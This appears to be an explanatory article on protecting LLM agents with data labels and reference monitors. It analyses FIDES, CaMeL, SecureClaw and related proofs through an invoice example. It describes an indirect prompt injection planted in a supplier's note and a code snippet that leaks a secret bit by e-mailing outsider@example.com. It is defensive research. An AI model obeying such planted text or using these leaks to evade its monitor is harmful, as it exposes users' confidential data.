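# Reliability of Information-Flow Controls and Tool Mediation in LLM Agent Security

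## Agents, data labels and checks on tool calls

Information-flow control and tool mediation are two ways to secure software agents built on large language models (LLMs). Information-flow control labels each piece of data by how confidential it is or how trustworthy its source is, and keeps the label attached as the data moves. Tool mediation places a trusted check between the agent and every action it can take. Both ideas come from research on shared computers in the 1970s and early 1980s. They are attractive for agents because the protection should hold even when the model makes a mistake or follows an attacker's instructions.

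An LLM on its own only produces text. An agent turns some of that text into actions by running a loop, which *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes step by step. Software sends the model the conversation so far and a list of tools, which are functions such as "send an e-mail", each with its parameters. The model returns either a final response or a tool call, which is a structured request to run one of the tools with arguments the model chooses. After a tool call, software runs the tool, appends the result to the conversation and queries the model again, until the model returns a final response. The model never executes anything itself. Ordinary code has to carry out or refuse each tool call, so a check can be added to that code.

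For example, a clerk named Ana might ask an agent to e-mail a new invoice to Ben, who approves payments at her company. The invoice contains a supplier name, an amount, a bank account number and a free-text note. The agent has four tools. `read_invoice` fetches the invoice, `send_email` sends mail, `export_pdf` turns an invoice into a PDF file, and `run_shell` runs commands on the machine. All but `read_invoice` are side-effecting tools, meaning they can change something outside the agent or send information to an outside party.

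Suppose the note, which the supplier wrote, contains a sentence telling any automated assistant to forward the full bank details to an outside address. The model receives the conversation as one stream of text, so the planted sentence reaches it in much the same form as Ana's request, and the model may comply. This is an indirect prompt injection, in which the attacker leaves instructions in data that the agent will later read, without ever communicating with the agent directly.

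### Why some designers stopped relying on the model

Developers have trained models to ignore instructions inside text marked as data, and have built detectors that look for such instructions. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, Nvidia and several universities, reviews these defences and finds that persistent attackers got past both kinds, as they had earlier got past defences for image classifiers. The paper conjectures that this will always be so, but concedes that model-level defences can substantially reduce the number of successful attacks. A lower success rate is still a poor guarantee against an attacker who can keep trying.

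Supporters of explicit rules outside the model also have an argument that does not depend on the attacker's skill. Natural-language instructions are ambiguous and a model's behaviour can vary from run to run, so an auditor has nothing fixed to verify when a permission depends on how the model reads a request. An explicit rule gives the auditor something fixed to check, although somebody still has to write a rule that captures what the company wants.

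The other common fallback is to ask a person to approve each action. Microsoft's engineering post *Information-flow control* argues that approval prompts scale poorly and wear down the vigilance they depend on. It also advises designers to assume that anything an agent can do at a user's request, it can also do because of a model's mistake or an attacker's injection.

The alternative is to treat the agent runtime, meaning the model and the software that plan and propose tool calls, as untrusted, the way an operating system treats third-party programs. A separate set of trusted components, the security boundary, controls what data the runtime may see and which actions it may cause. FIDES, the planner that Costa and colleagues built, and CaMeL, which runs model-written plans through a policy-enforcing interpreter, both follow this approach. Both need the security boundary to have correct information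 about the data and control over the actions, but they don't need the model to recognise the sentence in the supplier's note as an attack.

### Labels and how they combine

A confidentiality label restricts where data may go. The simplest scheme has two values, public and secret, while a richer one lists the people who may read the data. An integrity label records whether the data comes from a trusted or an untrusted source. Ana's request is trusted, and the supplier's note is untrusted even if it looks harmless.

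Most data in an agent combines several inputs, so the scheme needs a rule for labeling the result. *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) provides one. The model has a set of security classes, a relation that defines which classes may flow into which, and an operator that gives the class of any result computed from two inputs. Denning showed that, for the model to be consistent, the operator must return the least upper bound of the input classes, which is the least restrictive class that is at least as restrictive as both. A value computed from inputs a₁ to aₙ may flow into a destination b only if the combined class of all the inputs may flow into the class of b.

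When labels have only two values, combining secret and public data gives secret data, and combining untrusted and trusted data gives untrusted data. When labels are lists of permitted readers, the combined label is the intersection of the lists. In an example from Microsoft's post, an agent answers the inbox of a user named Alex. One message, from Priya, previews the quarterly sales, and another is from Marco, who is curious about them. A reply that draws on both messages has the readers {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so the agent may not send it to Marco on its own. The same rule that blocks theft also blocks this accidental leak, which involves no attacker.

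Taint tracking applies this rule automatically while a program runs. In the version that Costa and colleagues describe, each tool result has a label, and the conversation carries the combination of all the labels in it. Whatever the model writes next, including any tool calls it proposes, inherits that combined label. A tool's output takes the combined label of its arguments and all the stored data the tool may have read.

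Tracking labels through the model is imprecise because no one can yet reliably tell which parts of a long conversation influenced a given sentence. The safe assumption is that all of them did, so labels tend to become more restrictive as a task goes on. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes the end state as label explosion, in which every item carries every label and the labels no longer distinguish one item from another. This buildup of labels is one source of over-marking, which means treating ordinary data as protected.

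One remedy is to keep sensitive or untrusted values out of the conversation. The boundary stores the value and gives the runtime a reference ID that only trusted components can exchange for the value. The runtime can pass the ID to a tool without reading the value.

### Noninterference and deliberate release

Labels are a mechanism, and it helps to state separately what they are meant to achieve. The classical statement is noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*, defined for a machine that accepts commands from several users and shows each of them some output. Take any sequence of commands w and strike out every command that a group G issued, leaving purge(w). The group does not interfere with an observer u if, for every w,

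out(w, u) = out(purge(w), u).

u sees the same thing whether or not the group did anything. For data in an agent, this means comparing two runs. If the runs differ only in the account number on the invoice, an unauthorised person should not be able to observe any difference between them.

That standard is hard to meet because information can travel without being copied. Denning's example is the statement "if a = 0 then b := 0", where b starts with some other value. Anyone who inspects b afterwards learns whether a was zero, even if the assignment never ran. She called this an implicit flow, and a direct copy an explicit flow. She left out covert channels, such as a secret that shows only in how heavily a process loads the system. In the invoice case, if an agent writes to Ben only about amounts above 10,000 euros, anyone who can see that it sent a message learns something about the amount.

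The taint tracking described above controls only explicit flows, a limit that Costa and colleagues openly accept. They say full noninterference would come close to banning every tool that may write to a public place once any tool may have read a secret, and few useful agents could work under that ban.

Companies sometimes need to share protected data. To pay a supplier, for example, a company has to give its bank the supplier's account number. Declassification is a deliberate, declared release of some information from protected data, such as the last four digits of an account number. Endorsement, its counterpart for integrity, is a declared decision to treat some untrusted data as trusted for a stated purpose, for example after the data has matched a purchase order. Both deliberately weaken the guarantee, so it matters who can trigger them. Microsoft's prototype policy for chat messages lets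 a message go to people outside its reader list only if the request arose in a trusted context, so that an injected instruction cannot trigger the release.

### The reference monitor

Rules about data labels have no effect unless something enforces them when a program acts. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972) described the component that does this. The United States Air Force wanted people with different clearances to share one computer, and Anderson's panel assumed that some of them would be malicious users who had legitimate access and could run their own programs. An agent runtime that has read a hostile document is in a similar position, because it is already inside the system and has permissions that somebody gave it.

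Anderson's answer was the reference monitor, which checks every reference a program makes to data, devices or other programs against a list of what that program may do. The mechanism had to be tamper-proof, run on every reference, and be small enough to analyze and test completely. Importantly for tools, he added that if the system suspends the check for some programs, those programs become part of the security apparatus and must themselves meet the requirements for tamper resistance and analysis.

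Three years later, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, Saltzer and Schroeder named the requirement of constant checking "complete mediation", the term still used. Under this principle, the system must check that every access to every object is authorized, including during start-up, recovery, shutdown and maintenance. They warned against reusing the result of an earlier check, because permissions may have changed. They also recommended denying access by default and using explicit rules to allow it.

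In an agent, the monitor sits where tool calls become actions. A sink is a point where data leaves or an action takes effect, such as the interface to the mail server. Costa and colleagues give two policies that a monitor can apply at sinks. The first, an integrity policy, allows a consequential call only if the call and its arguments carry trusted labels. The second allows data out through a channel only if everyone who can read the channel is on the data's reader list. For e-mail, they allow a looser integrity policy, in which the decision to send and the recipient must be trusted but the message text need not be.

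### One invoice, three runs

Ana's company adopts these rules. Its policy makes the account number a protected field, which the runtime must not read or release in plaintext. Ben decides on the amount and doesn't need the full number, so a declared exception lets him see the last four digits. The invoice is labeled as follows.

| Field | Who may read it | Integrity | What the runtime receives |
|---|---|---|---|
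| Supplier name | Ana, Ben | trusted after a match with the purchase order | the name |
| Amount | Ana, Ben | trusted after a match with the purchase order | the amount |
| Account number | payment system only | trusted after a match with the supplier record | a reference ID |
| Free-text note | Ana, Ben | untrusted | a reference ID |

When everything works correctly, the runtime calls `read_invoice` and receives the name, the amount and two tokens. It then proposes an e-mail to Ben containing the name, the amount, the last four digits and the note's token. The monitor finds that Ben's address came from Ana and that nothing untrusted has entered the conversation, so the call and the recipient are trusted. Ben is on the reader list of every item in the message. A trusted mail component replaces the note's token with its text and sends the message, so the planted instruction reaches Ben as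 an odd sentence in an e-mail without passing through the model.

If the runtime had put the account number's own token into the message for exchange, the combined reader list would have been {Ana, Ben} ∩ {payment system}, which is empty, so the monitor would have refused the call. Opening the note would have made the conversation untrusted, and the monitor would then have refused any later e-mail, including legitimate ones, which is one drawback of this approach. The monitor also refuses a call to `run_shell`, because no rule allows it for this task.

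**The account number without its label.** Now a supplier uses a new template that puts the number in a field called "remit to", and the labelling rule looks only for "account number". The system treats unlabelled fields as ordinary data, so the runtime receives the number in the clear and includes it in the message. The monitor combines the labels it has, gets {Ana, Ben}, and lets the e-mail through. It applies every rule correctly, but the labels describe the data wrongly. The number also stays in the conversation history and in any memory the runtime shares with other agents. These are internal channels, meaning routes inside the system that the final e-mail does not show.

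A missed field is a protected field that the system wrongly treats as ordinary. The opposite error, treating an ordinary field as protected, is far easier to spot. If the rule had let only the payment system read the amount, Ben's e-mail would have been blocked and Ana would have complained the same afternoon. Saltzer and Schroeder noticed that, in access rules generally, a mistake that refuses access is found quickly, while one that allows access may go unnoticed in normal use. Marking all unlabelled data as secret would have caught the number, but it would also have caused more refusals like the one about the amount.

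**A public link from an unmonitored tool.** In the last run the labels are again correct, but Ana asks for the invoice as a PDF. The developers registered `export_pdf` as a formatting tool with no outside effects, so its calls skip the monitor. The tool opens the stored invoice, renders the whole page, including the account number, uploads the file to a hosting service and returns a link that anyone can open. The runtime then proposes an e-mail to Ben containing the link. The monitor approves it because the text is short and the recipient is permitted, but the account number is already on the public web. The reference ID did not prevent the leak, because `export_pdf` read the number directly from the stored invoice, without needing it from the runtime.

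Even if the call had gone through the monitor, a rule that described the tool as writing a local file would not have stopped the upload, because the upload happens inside the tool after the monitor has made its decision. Anderson found the same weakness in GCOS III, a commercial operating system of his day. Hardware confined each user's program to its own area of memory, but the program relied on the system's supervisor for input and output, and the supervisor ran with that confinement switched off. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* allows the monitor to consist of several enforcement points, such as a gateway for tool calls and a proxy that inspects outgoing network traffic, provided that together they cover every security-relevant action. Such a proxy could have stopped the upload. `run_shell` makes the problem harder because a single command can read files and open network connections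 in ways that are not apparent from its text.

The protection therefore depends on correct labels and complete mediation. Labels are correct if every protected field carries a label at least as restrictive as the policy requires, from the moment it enters the system and through every copy, summary and change of format. Mediation is complete if every relevant read and every outside effect passes through the check, including effects that a tool produces after the monitor has approved the call. Neither condition is enough alone, since the upload happened despite correct labels, and a check on every sink would still have let the unlabelled account number through.

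## What the security proofs assume

Each published security proof for agents shows that some kind of leak or unauthorised action cannot happen as long as its premises about labels, tools and trusted code hold. Those premises include correct labels and complete mediation in some form, often alongside others that are easier to overlook. The FIDES, CaMeL and SecureClaw designs put the trusted check in different places, so they rely on different assumptions about Ana's invoice system.

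### FIDES: labels in the planner's conversation

FIDES, by Costa and colleagues, adds labels to the ordinary agent loop, in which the model chooses one tool call at a time. It splits the loop into a planner and a planning loop. The planner takes the latest message and returns one of three actions: query the model, call a tool, or finish with an answer. The planning loop carries out the action, checks the policy before every tool call, and labels the result.

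To label the result of a tool f, the loop needs the set of stored data that f may read, R(f), and the set that f may change, W(f). The formal model takes these sets as given, but in a real system someone has to declare them. If the declaration for `export_pdf` lists the supplier name and the amount but omits the account number, the loop gives the finished file too permissive a label, and every later check relies on that label.

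FIDES hides some data from the model so that the first untrusted result doesn't restrict the whole conversation. When `read_invoice` returns, the planner checks whether each field's label is more restrictive than the conversation's current label. If it is, the planner stores the field in its memory under a new variable name and shows the model only that name, so the conversation keeps its old label. When the model later uses the variable name in a tool call, the planner substitutes the stored value and its label. A single call can therefore combine a trusted decision to e-mail Ben with an untrusted note in the message body. In the experiments, Costa and colleagues hid fields only when the integrity label required it and left confidentiality to the policy checks, so the model could still read trusted secrets.

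Some tasks depend on what a hidden field contains. For example, Ana might ask the agent to pay early if the supplier's note offers a discount. The planner can pass the note to a second model, which has no tools and must answer in a fixed format such as true or false. FIDES records the format in the answer's label. A true-or-false answer carries at most one bit, so a policy may let it influence a payment even though the note is untrusted. One bit can still do harm, because the supplier wrote the note and can therefore decide whether the company pays early.

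The formal guarantee for confidentiality is explicit secrecy. For a given run, let g be the combined effect of its steps on the stored data. If two versions of the data, d₁ and d₂, agree on everything public, then g(d₁) and g(d₂) must also agree on everything public. The definition keeps the steps fixed while the secret changes, so it rules out copying a secret account number into a public file. It allows the choice of steps to depend on the secret, so it permits implicit flows that noninterference forbids. It also treats the model as deterministic and does not cover side channels such as timing.

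For integrity, Costa and colleagues rely on the policy that consequential calls need trusted labels, and they state no comparable theorem. In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) credit FIDES with a noninterference theorem for its one agent loop, which is more than Costa and colleagues claim for confidentiality. Garby and colleagues also object that FIDES's deliberate exceptions are hard to audit. When a true-or-false answer derived from protected data passes a check, a reviewer looking at that run cannot tell an intended release from a leak. They acknowledge that the FIDES experiments never used this exception.

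Costa and colleagues' guarantee assumes that labels come with the data or that software can infer them. Inference can go wrong, as in their example of treating an e-mail's sender and recipients as its only readers when someone may have shared it more widely. They tested their system on AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking, travel and chat tasks with planted instructions, and marked a kind of field as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it. With policy checks on, no attack got past the policies. This is good evidence that the enforcement works, but it doesn't test the labelling, because the experimenters, unlike Ana's company, knew in advance where the attacks would be.

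### CaMeL: a plan that runs in an interpreter

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues designed, builds on Simon Willison's dual-LLM pattern. A privileged planning model reads Ana's request and writes a program to carry it out, but never reads untrusted data directly. When the program needs something from the supplier's note, it passes the note to a quarantined model, which returns a value and cannot call tools. An interpreter runs the program, tracks labels on its values, and checks a policy before each sensitive tool call.

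The separation protects the plan because the privileged model wrote the program without seeing the note, so the sentence planted there cannot add a step. The note can still supply a bad value. If Ana asks the agent to reply to whatever address the supplier gives, the supplier chooses the recipient, and only the label on that address can stop the e-mail. CaMeL therefore depends on correct label tracking, but it has no published soundness theorem comparable to the one for FIDES. The CaMeL paper names formalisation as a crucial direction for further work.

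Garby and colleagues examined the tracking and found two ways for secrets to escape. The first is a version of a problem that the computer scientist J. S. Fenton described in 1974. Applied to the invoice, it looks like this:

```
small = True
large = True
if amount > 10000: small = False
if small: large = False
if large: send_email("outsider@example.com", "large invoice")
```

Suppose the amount is 12,000 euros. The third line sets `small` to false and labels it secret, since the change depended on the amount. The test on the fourth line fails, so the interpreter skips the assignment and `large` keeps its original value and public label. Because the last line tests a public value, the policy allows the e-mail. If the amount is 8,000 euros, the fourth line sets `large` to false and no e-mail is sent. The outsider can tell which case holds by whether the e-mail arrives. CaMeL raises a variable's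 label only on the branch that runs, so it misses the information revealed by the skipped branch.

The second leak is outside the interpreter, in an ordinary Python loop that starts another attempt when a program fails. The loop does not track labels. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one bit. Most information-flow systems tolerate a one-bit leak, but here each attempt can reveal a different bit, and about 67 attempts would be enough to recover a 20-digit account number. Garby and colleagues also report a simpler fault, which is that CaMeL treats text as trusted even after a program inserts an untrusted value into it.

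These are gaps in the guarantee, and an attacker would still have to find a way to exploit them. The privileged model normally writes its program before untrusted text can influence it. The retry loop weakens that protection because error messages from one attempt feed into the next. CaMeL censors those messages to reduce the risk, but offers no formal guarantee.

### SecureClaw: reference IDs and exact approval

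*SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) assumes that an attacker may control the entire runtime. Its design puts four trusted components outside the runtime: a gateway that handles reads, a store for protected values, a policy engine, and an executor. Only the executor can call the interfaces that act on the outside world.

When the runtime reads the invoice, the gateway puts the protected values into the store and returns reference IDs. Each ID is an unpredictable string, computed with a secret key from a fresh random value, the session and the object. It is neither an encrypted copy of the account number nor a hash of it, so the runtime cannot recover the number from the ID. The store also records who may use the ID, in which session, until when, for which version of the object, and at which destinations trusted code may exchange it for the value.

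Sending the e-mail takes two phases, called preview and commit. The runtime first proposes the kind of action and its inputs. The gateway adds the authenticated caller, the session and the context, such as the recipient and the version of the invoice. It writes the whole request ρ in a fixed format, Canon(ρ), and computes a keyed fingerprint of the result,

h = HMAC-SHA256(k, Canon(ρ)).

The policy engine ties its decision to the fingerprint h. At commit, the executor recomputes h from the request it received. It also checks that the approval is genuine, recent and unused, and that Ana has confirmed the request if the policy requires it. If every check passes, the executor replaces the reference IDs with their values and sends the message. If the runtime changes Ben's address after approval, the fingerprint no longer matches and the executor refuses the request.

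Theorem 1 concerns this commit step. The attacker controls the runtime and may request as many previews and commits as it likes. It wins if the executor accepts a request that the policy never approved, one that differs from the approved request, or one that the executor has already accepted. Ma and Schmid prove that

Pr[attacker wins] ≤ Adv(MAC) + ε(q).

The first term is the chance of forging an approval. The second is the chance that two different requests among the q in the attack share a fingerprint. Both are negligible with standard cryptography. The theorem needs the following premises.

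| Premise of Theorem 1 | What it requires when Ana e-mails Ben |
|---|---|
| Attackers cannot forge approvals, and different requests almost never share a fingerprint | The cryptography is sound and its keys stay secret |
| Gateway and executor encode requests identically | Both produce the same text for the same e-mail |
| Equal encodings at one sink mean equal outside effects | Two e-mails with the same encoding reach the same people with the same content |
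| The request includes every field that can change the effect | It lists all recipients, the attachments and the invoice version |
| A required confirmation belongs to one request | Ana's click on one e-mail cannot release another |
| Approvals expire and work only once, even after a crash | A restart does not send the e-mail twice |
| Every sink with outside effects sits behind the executor | `export_pdf` cannot upload a file by itself |

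The premises about encoding are hard to meet. Suppose Ana sends the invoice to a mailing list for approvers, and the request contains only the list's address. After the policy engine approves the request, someone adds an outsider to the list. The encoding and the fingerprint stay the same, so the executor accepts the request, but the e-mail also reaches the outsider. Theorem 1 does not cover this case, because equal encodings no longer mean equal effects. Ma and Schmid ask that the encoding include the set of recipients and version numbers for anything that can change, but developers can only add version numbers for things they know can change.

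The proof first rules out forged approvals and then shared fingerprints, and each step adds one term to the bound. It assumes the remaining premises. The bound does not include the chance that a developer forgot to route a tool through the executor, so a small bound does not mean the deployed system is unlikely to fail. The theorem also does not cover requests that the policy allows but Ana did not intend, such as an e-mail to the wrong approver.

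Theorem 2 concerns what the runtime can learn about a protected value when it receives only a reference ID and harmless metadata. The attacker picks two values, the system stores one of them, and the attacker tries to find out which. With IDs of κ bits, N valid IDs at a time and q guesses, everything the runtime sees could have come from someone who knew only the metadata, apart from an advantage of at most

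min(1, qN / 2^κ) + ε.

Here ε covers any weakness in how the system generates the IDs, and is zero if they are truly random. A million guesses against a thousand valid 128-bit IDs would succeed with probability at most about 3 × 10⁻³⁰. The proof assumes that failed guesses reveal only a refusal, that only trusted components can exchange an ID for its value, that every sensitive read goes through the gateway, and that the gateway classifies protected fields correctly.

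The account number under "remit to" violates the last premise because the gateway misses it. Ma and Schmid explicitly exclude missed fields from their claim. They also measured leakage and found that it rises with the share of fields the gateway misses.

### What correctly labelled data can reveal

Theorem 2 describes a stricter system than the one Ma and Schmid tested. A model that sees only reference IDs cannot do much planning, and current benchmarks require the model to read text. The tested gateway therefore sends a short summary D(v) with the ID of each protected value v. The summary is a declared release, and fixed rules produce it without a language model. The rules keep up to eight fields or items from each container and cut each text field to 512 characters. They also replace e-mail addresses, account numbers and web addresses with tokens, and remove certain suspicious markers and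 tags.

Theorem 3 limits what these summaries add to the attacker's knowledge. For two possible values v₀ and v₁, let Δ be the total variation distance between their summaries. It is 0 if the summaries give no way to tell the values apart and 1 if they always do. Over m reads, the attacker's advantage is at most

min(1, Δ₁ + Δ₂ + … + Δₘ)

plus twice the bound from Theorem 2. If the summary never changes, every Δ is zero and the system is back to bare reference IDs. If the summary is a full copy, the bound is 1 and guarantees nothing. The sum also grows with the number of reads, and the theorem requires that no hidden state connect one summary to the next. For this reason SecureClaw resets its replacement tokens at each read.

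Ma and Schmid tested the actual rules on 122 pairs of inputs in 19 categories, building each pair to differ in exactly one sensitive place. Because the rules are deterministic, the distance between a pair's summaries was 0 if they were identical and 1 if they differed. The summaries differed in 35 pairs, so the mean distance was 0.287. In the worst categories, every pair differed, so the mean was 1.

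That mean depends on how many pairs of each kind the researchers chose, and they warn against reading it as a limit on leakage. The results for each category are more useful to a user. The rules hid every change to a properly formed e-mail address, bank account number or web address. They also hid text beyond the 512th character and list items beyond the eighth. They revealed every change to the opening text of a message, a subject line, the first eight items of a list, or a business partner's name in plain text. They also failed on identifiers that were malformed in ambiguous ways.

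In Ana's case, the gateway could apply every label correctly, marking the free-text note as protected, and still pass most of the note on in the summary, a channel that the designers opened on purpose. If the supplier writes in the first sentence that it is close to insolvency, the summary contains that sentence, and the runtime can copy it into a message to another agent or into shared memory. An account number in the standard format would become a token, but one with a typing error might not. Ma and Schmid prove that even when a summary reveals everything it can, the runtime gains no new access to the stored original and cannot send an unapproved e-mail.

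### A counterexample for each premise

*Ghost Tool Calls* (Mohammadi, Klein and colleagues, 2026) proves a shorter theorem that makes each premise's contribution easy to see. It studies agents that save time by making tool calls before they know whether they will need the results. If the agent later drops that line of work, the outside service has still received the request, which the paper calls a ghost tool call. Even a search that changes nothing can disclose information through its search terms or the choice of service, and the agent cannot take that information back.

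Their monitor therefore decides before a call leaves the system. It can allow the call, rewrite its arguments, use a trusted local substitute, postpone it, or block it. Let S be all the calls the agent issues and C those whose results or effects it ends up using. For an outside observer i, O(S) is what i records, and O(C) is what i would have recorded if the agent had issued only the calls in C from the start. The theorem concerns the difference,

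Δ = O(S) \ O(C),

which is a set of disclosures and has nothing to do with the distance Δ in SecureClaw. It states that no field which the policy forbids observer i to see can enter this difference, provided that three premises hold:

- Complete mediation (A1): every call reaches the outside only through the monitor, and no log, cache, retry queue or monitoring service receives the raw data first.
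- Label correctness (A2): the labels correctly classify each call's destination, arguments and type of effect.
- Action preservation (A3): rewrites and substitutes really remove what they claim to remove.

Mohammadi and colleagues state that each premise is necessary, and the invoice example shows why. Unlike Ma and Schmid, they trust the planner, so in this version the planner may handle the account number itself. Suppose that, while preparing Ana's e-mail, the planner predicts that Ben will ask whether the supplier's bank details are valid, and proposes a call to an outside verification service in advance. The policy allows such early calls to include the supplier's country but not its account number. Ben never asks, and the agent does not pursue the verification.

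Complete mediation fails if a debugging library records the arguments of every proposed call and sends them to a hosted logging company before the monitor has made a decision. The monitor then replaces the account number with the country, so the verification service receives only the country, but the logging company already has the number. The number leaks even though every label and the rewrite were correct. Developers rarely think of a debugging library as a tool with outside effects, so complete mediation is harder to achieve than a list of the agent's tools would suggest.

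**Without correct labels.** The supplier's new template puts the number under "remit to". The labelling rule treats this as a postal address and marks it public, so the monitor finds no forbidden label and lets the call through unchanged. This monitor postpones or blocks anything with a missing label, but that default doesn't protect against a wrong label.

**Without action preservation.** The account number is labeled correctly, and the monitor triggers a rewrite that should leave only the country code. The rewrite code keeps the characters before the first space and, if there are exactly four, shortens them to the country code. This works for account numbers written in groups of four, but this supplier writes the number without spaces, so the code returns the whole number. The monitor treats the result as harmless and sends it.

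Each case breaks one premise while the other two hold, so no premise follows from the other two. Once a premise fails, the theorem gives no assurance about the system as a whole, and somebody has to examine the violation to find out whether it causes a leak. Some violations don't. For example, a tool that bypasses the monitor but only rounds numbers on the local machine discloses nothing.

The theorem covers only the additional exposure from calls made too early, not what the agent's final choice of calls reveals. It also doesn't cover exposure to the company that hosts the model. If Ana's agent uses a model on someone else's servers, that company receives the conversation. Mohammadi and colleagues leave control over that route to future work.

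### What a proof can establish

Garby and colleagues designed a small programming language, LLMbda, to try to close the gaps they had found. Every value in it carries a label, and every step of a program passes labels on, including steps in code that a model has just written. They gave a computer-checked proof that inputs above a given label cannot affect results at or below it, except by determining whether the program finishes. The theorem covers every program in the language, so the retry loop that leaked in CaMeL can run inside the tracked system.

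Even this theorem needs a developer to label the sources correctly and put checks at the sinks. It also models tools and data sources as part of the program, which the paper lists as a limitation because real tools act on systems outside it. The language lets a program endorse untrusted data, or declare it trusted. In tests on AgentDojo's banking tasks, two of 1,296 attacked runs succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment it described, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The program endorsed the contents, and the payment went through. Without endorsement, the system blocked the attack but could not carry out legitimate requests of the same kind. The proof guarantees that endorsing untrusted data cannot expose secrets, but whether to trust a particular file depends on facts outside the program.

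Tests can support only the premises they exercise. Ma and Schmid attacked SecureClaw's commit step with forged approvals, altered recipients, expired approvals and repeated requests. The executor refused all 25 attacks and accepted all four legitimate requests. This is evidence that the implementation checks approvals as the theorem requires, but not that every sink sits behind the executor, because every attack was a request to the executor. The test could not have detected an `export_pdf` tool that uploads files directly. To check for one, Ana's company would need a complete inventory of the interfaces that can act on the outside world, and some assurance that the runtime can reach them only through the executor.

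The premise about labels has a similar limit. For Theorem 2, Ma and Schmid require the gateway to classify fields correctly according to the deployment's schema or policy. If the schema omits "remit to", a gateway can meet that requirement by following the schema perfectly and still give the runtime the account number. Checking the proof cannot reveal the omission, because the proof does not include what the company meant to protect.

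A proof still narrows the search after a failure. If the protected account number turns up outside Ana's company by a route that the theorem covers, at least one of the premises was false, barring broken cryptography or an extraordinarily lucky guess. Investigators can check the field's label, the tools that handled it and the encoding of the request without reconstructing why the model proposed the action. The company can check the same things before it deploys the system. Ma and Schmid call false assurance the main risk of deployment, because the guarantees lapse when either condition fails, even though the theorems remain true.

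## Experiments with sensitive fields that are missed or mislabelled

To test how much depends on correct labels, researchers have made some labels wrong on purpose and counted what leaks. Ma and Schmid ran the most detailed such experiment, using SecureClaw and AgentLeak, a benchmark for privacy leaks in systems where several agents work together. AgentLeak has 996 scenarios, 496 of which contain an attack. Each scenario has a privacy rule that says which fields are protected, so the experimenters could check the labels against it, but Ana's company has no such reference for its invoices.

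In these experiments, a leak meant that the actual value of a protected field appeared in the final answer, in a message between agents or in shared memory. AgentLeak's own scorer, which uses a different test, found leaks in 16 of the 496 attacked scenarios in SecureClaw's main run, 15 of them in the final answer. The check for actual values found none as long as the gateway marked every protected field, so any leak it found later came from a missed field.

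### Random misses

Ma and Schmid made the gateway miss protected fields at random, at four nominal rates. The answer key contains 44,799 protected fields, or about 45 per task, so even a low miss rate affects many tasks. If misses are independent and happen at rate m, a task with 45 protected fields has at least one miss with probability 1 − (1 − m)⁴⁵. The middle column below is calculated from that formula, and the last column shows what Ma and Schmid measured.

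| Protected fields missed | Tasks with at least one miss (calculated) | Attacked scenarios with a leak (measured) |
|---|---|---|
| 1% | 36% | 18 of 496 (3.6%) |
| 5% | 90% | 44 of 496 (8.9%) |
| 10% | 99% | 65 of 496 (13.1%) |
| 20% | over 99.9% | 85 of 496 (17.1%) |

At a 1% miss rate, more than a third of tasks would give the runtime at least one protected value in plaintext, yet fewer than 4% of attacked scenarios showed a leak. The leak rate is lower because a model doesn't repeat everything it reads. Suppose the runtime reads the account number on Ana's invoice and then writes to Ben only about the amount. The number is now in the model's conversation, possibly on another company's servers, but not in any of the three channels that the leak check searches. The check also looks only for concrete values, so it could overlook a number that the model encoded or described in other words.

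The number of leaking scenarios grew more slowly than the number of missed fields. With 45 fields in each of 496 scenarios, a 1% miss rate means about 220 missed fields, and one scenario leaked for every 12 of these. At 20%, about 4,460 fields were missed, and one scenario leaked for every 53. If every missed field had the same small chance of leaking, the number of leaking scenarios would have risen almost in proportion. The slower growth may be because a minority of scenarios lead the agents to pass on nearly anything they can read. One miss would be enough to cause a leak in such a scenario, and further misses would not raise the number of leaking scenarios.

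The ratio of leaks to misses probably depends heavily on the agent. An agent with no protection leaked in 94% of the attacked scenarios when measured with AgentLeak's own scorer. In a smaller test, Ma and Schmid switched off SecureClaw's reference IDs entirely, and only 5 of 24 attacked scenarios leaked through messages between agents. They designed SecureClaw for an attacker who controls the runtime. Such an attacker can copy out every value the runtime receives, so the calculated column is a better guide to that case than the measured one.

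The agents still completed at least 81% of tasks at every miss rate, so a company that monitored only task completion would not have noticed the misses.

Over-marking fields was far less harmful than missing them. Ma and Schmid marked up to 20% of the ordinary fields as protected while missing none of the protected ones. No scenario leaked at any level they tried, and the agents completed between 81.6% and 82.2% of tasks. Over-marking had little effect on task completion because SecureClaw's runtime can still pass an over-marked field's reference ID to a tool.

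That ability is important for the agent's usefulness. In a separate test on AgentDojo, Ma and Schmid switched off the step that turns tokens back into values, and the number of ordinary tasks completed fell from 55 to 45 out of 97. Some of the loss may reflect the scoring, because the benchmark expects exact text. A system that simply blocks protected data could lose more from over-marking.

### From fields to whole tasks

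Real labelling errors are unlikely to be random because they have causes, such as an unusual field name. Ma and Schmid therefore also audited a detector that decides which fields to protect. Its inputs are the privacy instruction, the type of application, the names of records and fields, and the declared data types, but not the values or the answer key. The researchers finalised its decisions before scoring them.

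The detector found 44,448 of the 44,799 protected fields, a recall of 99.22%, but it found every protected field in only 879 of the 996 tasks, or 88%. In the other 117 tasks, at least one protected field would have reached the runtime unprotected. For a company that needs every invoice to stay confidential, the per-task rate matters more than the recall.

The two figures also show how the errors were distributed. The detector missed 0.78% of protected fields. If those misses had been independent, with 45 fields in every task, the share of fully covered tasks would have been

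(1 − 0.0078)⁴⁵ ≈ 0.70,

or about 700 tasks. The actual count was 879, so the misses were concentrated in fewer tasks. The 351 misses fell in 117 tasks, an average of exactly three each, whereas independent misses would have fallen in nearly 300 tasks.

Some of this clustering could come from differences in task size, since a task with few fields has few chances for a miss, but that effect is usually modest. If half the tasks had 10 protected fields and half had 80, independent misses would leave 73% of tasks fully covered, still well below 88%. Task sizes would have to be very unevenly distributed to explain the remaining gap.

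A shared cause is a more natural explanation. A detector that misreads "remit to" on one invoice will probably misread it on every invoice that uses the same template. Clustering therefore reduces the number of affected tasks but makes the failures repeatable. Ana's company might handle hundreds of invoices correctly but expose the account number on every invoice from one supplier. A spot check of other suppliers' invoices wouldn't find the problem.

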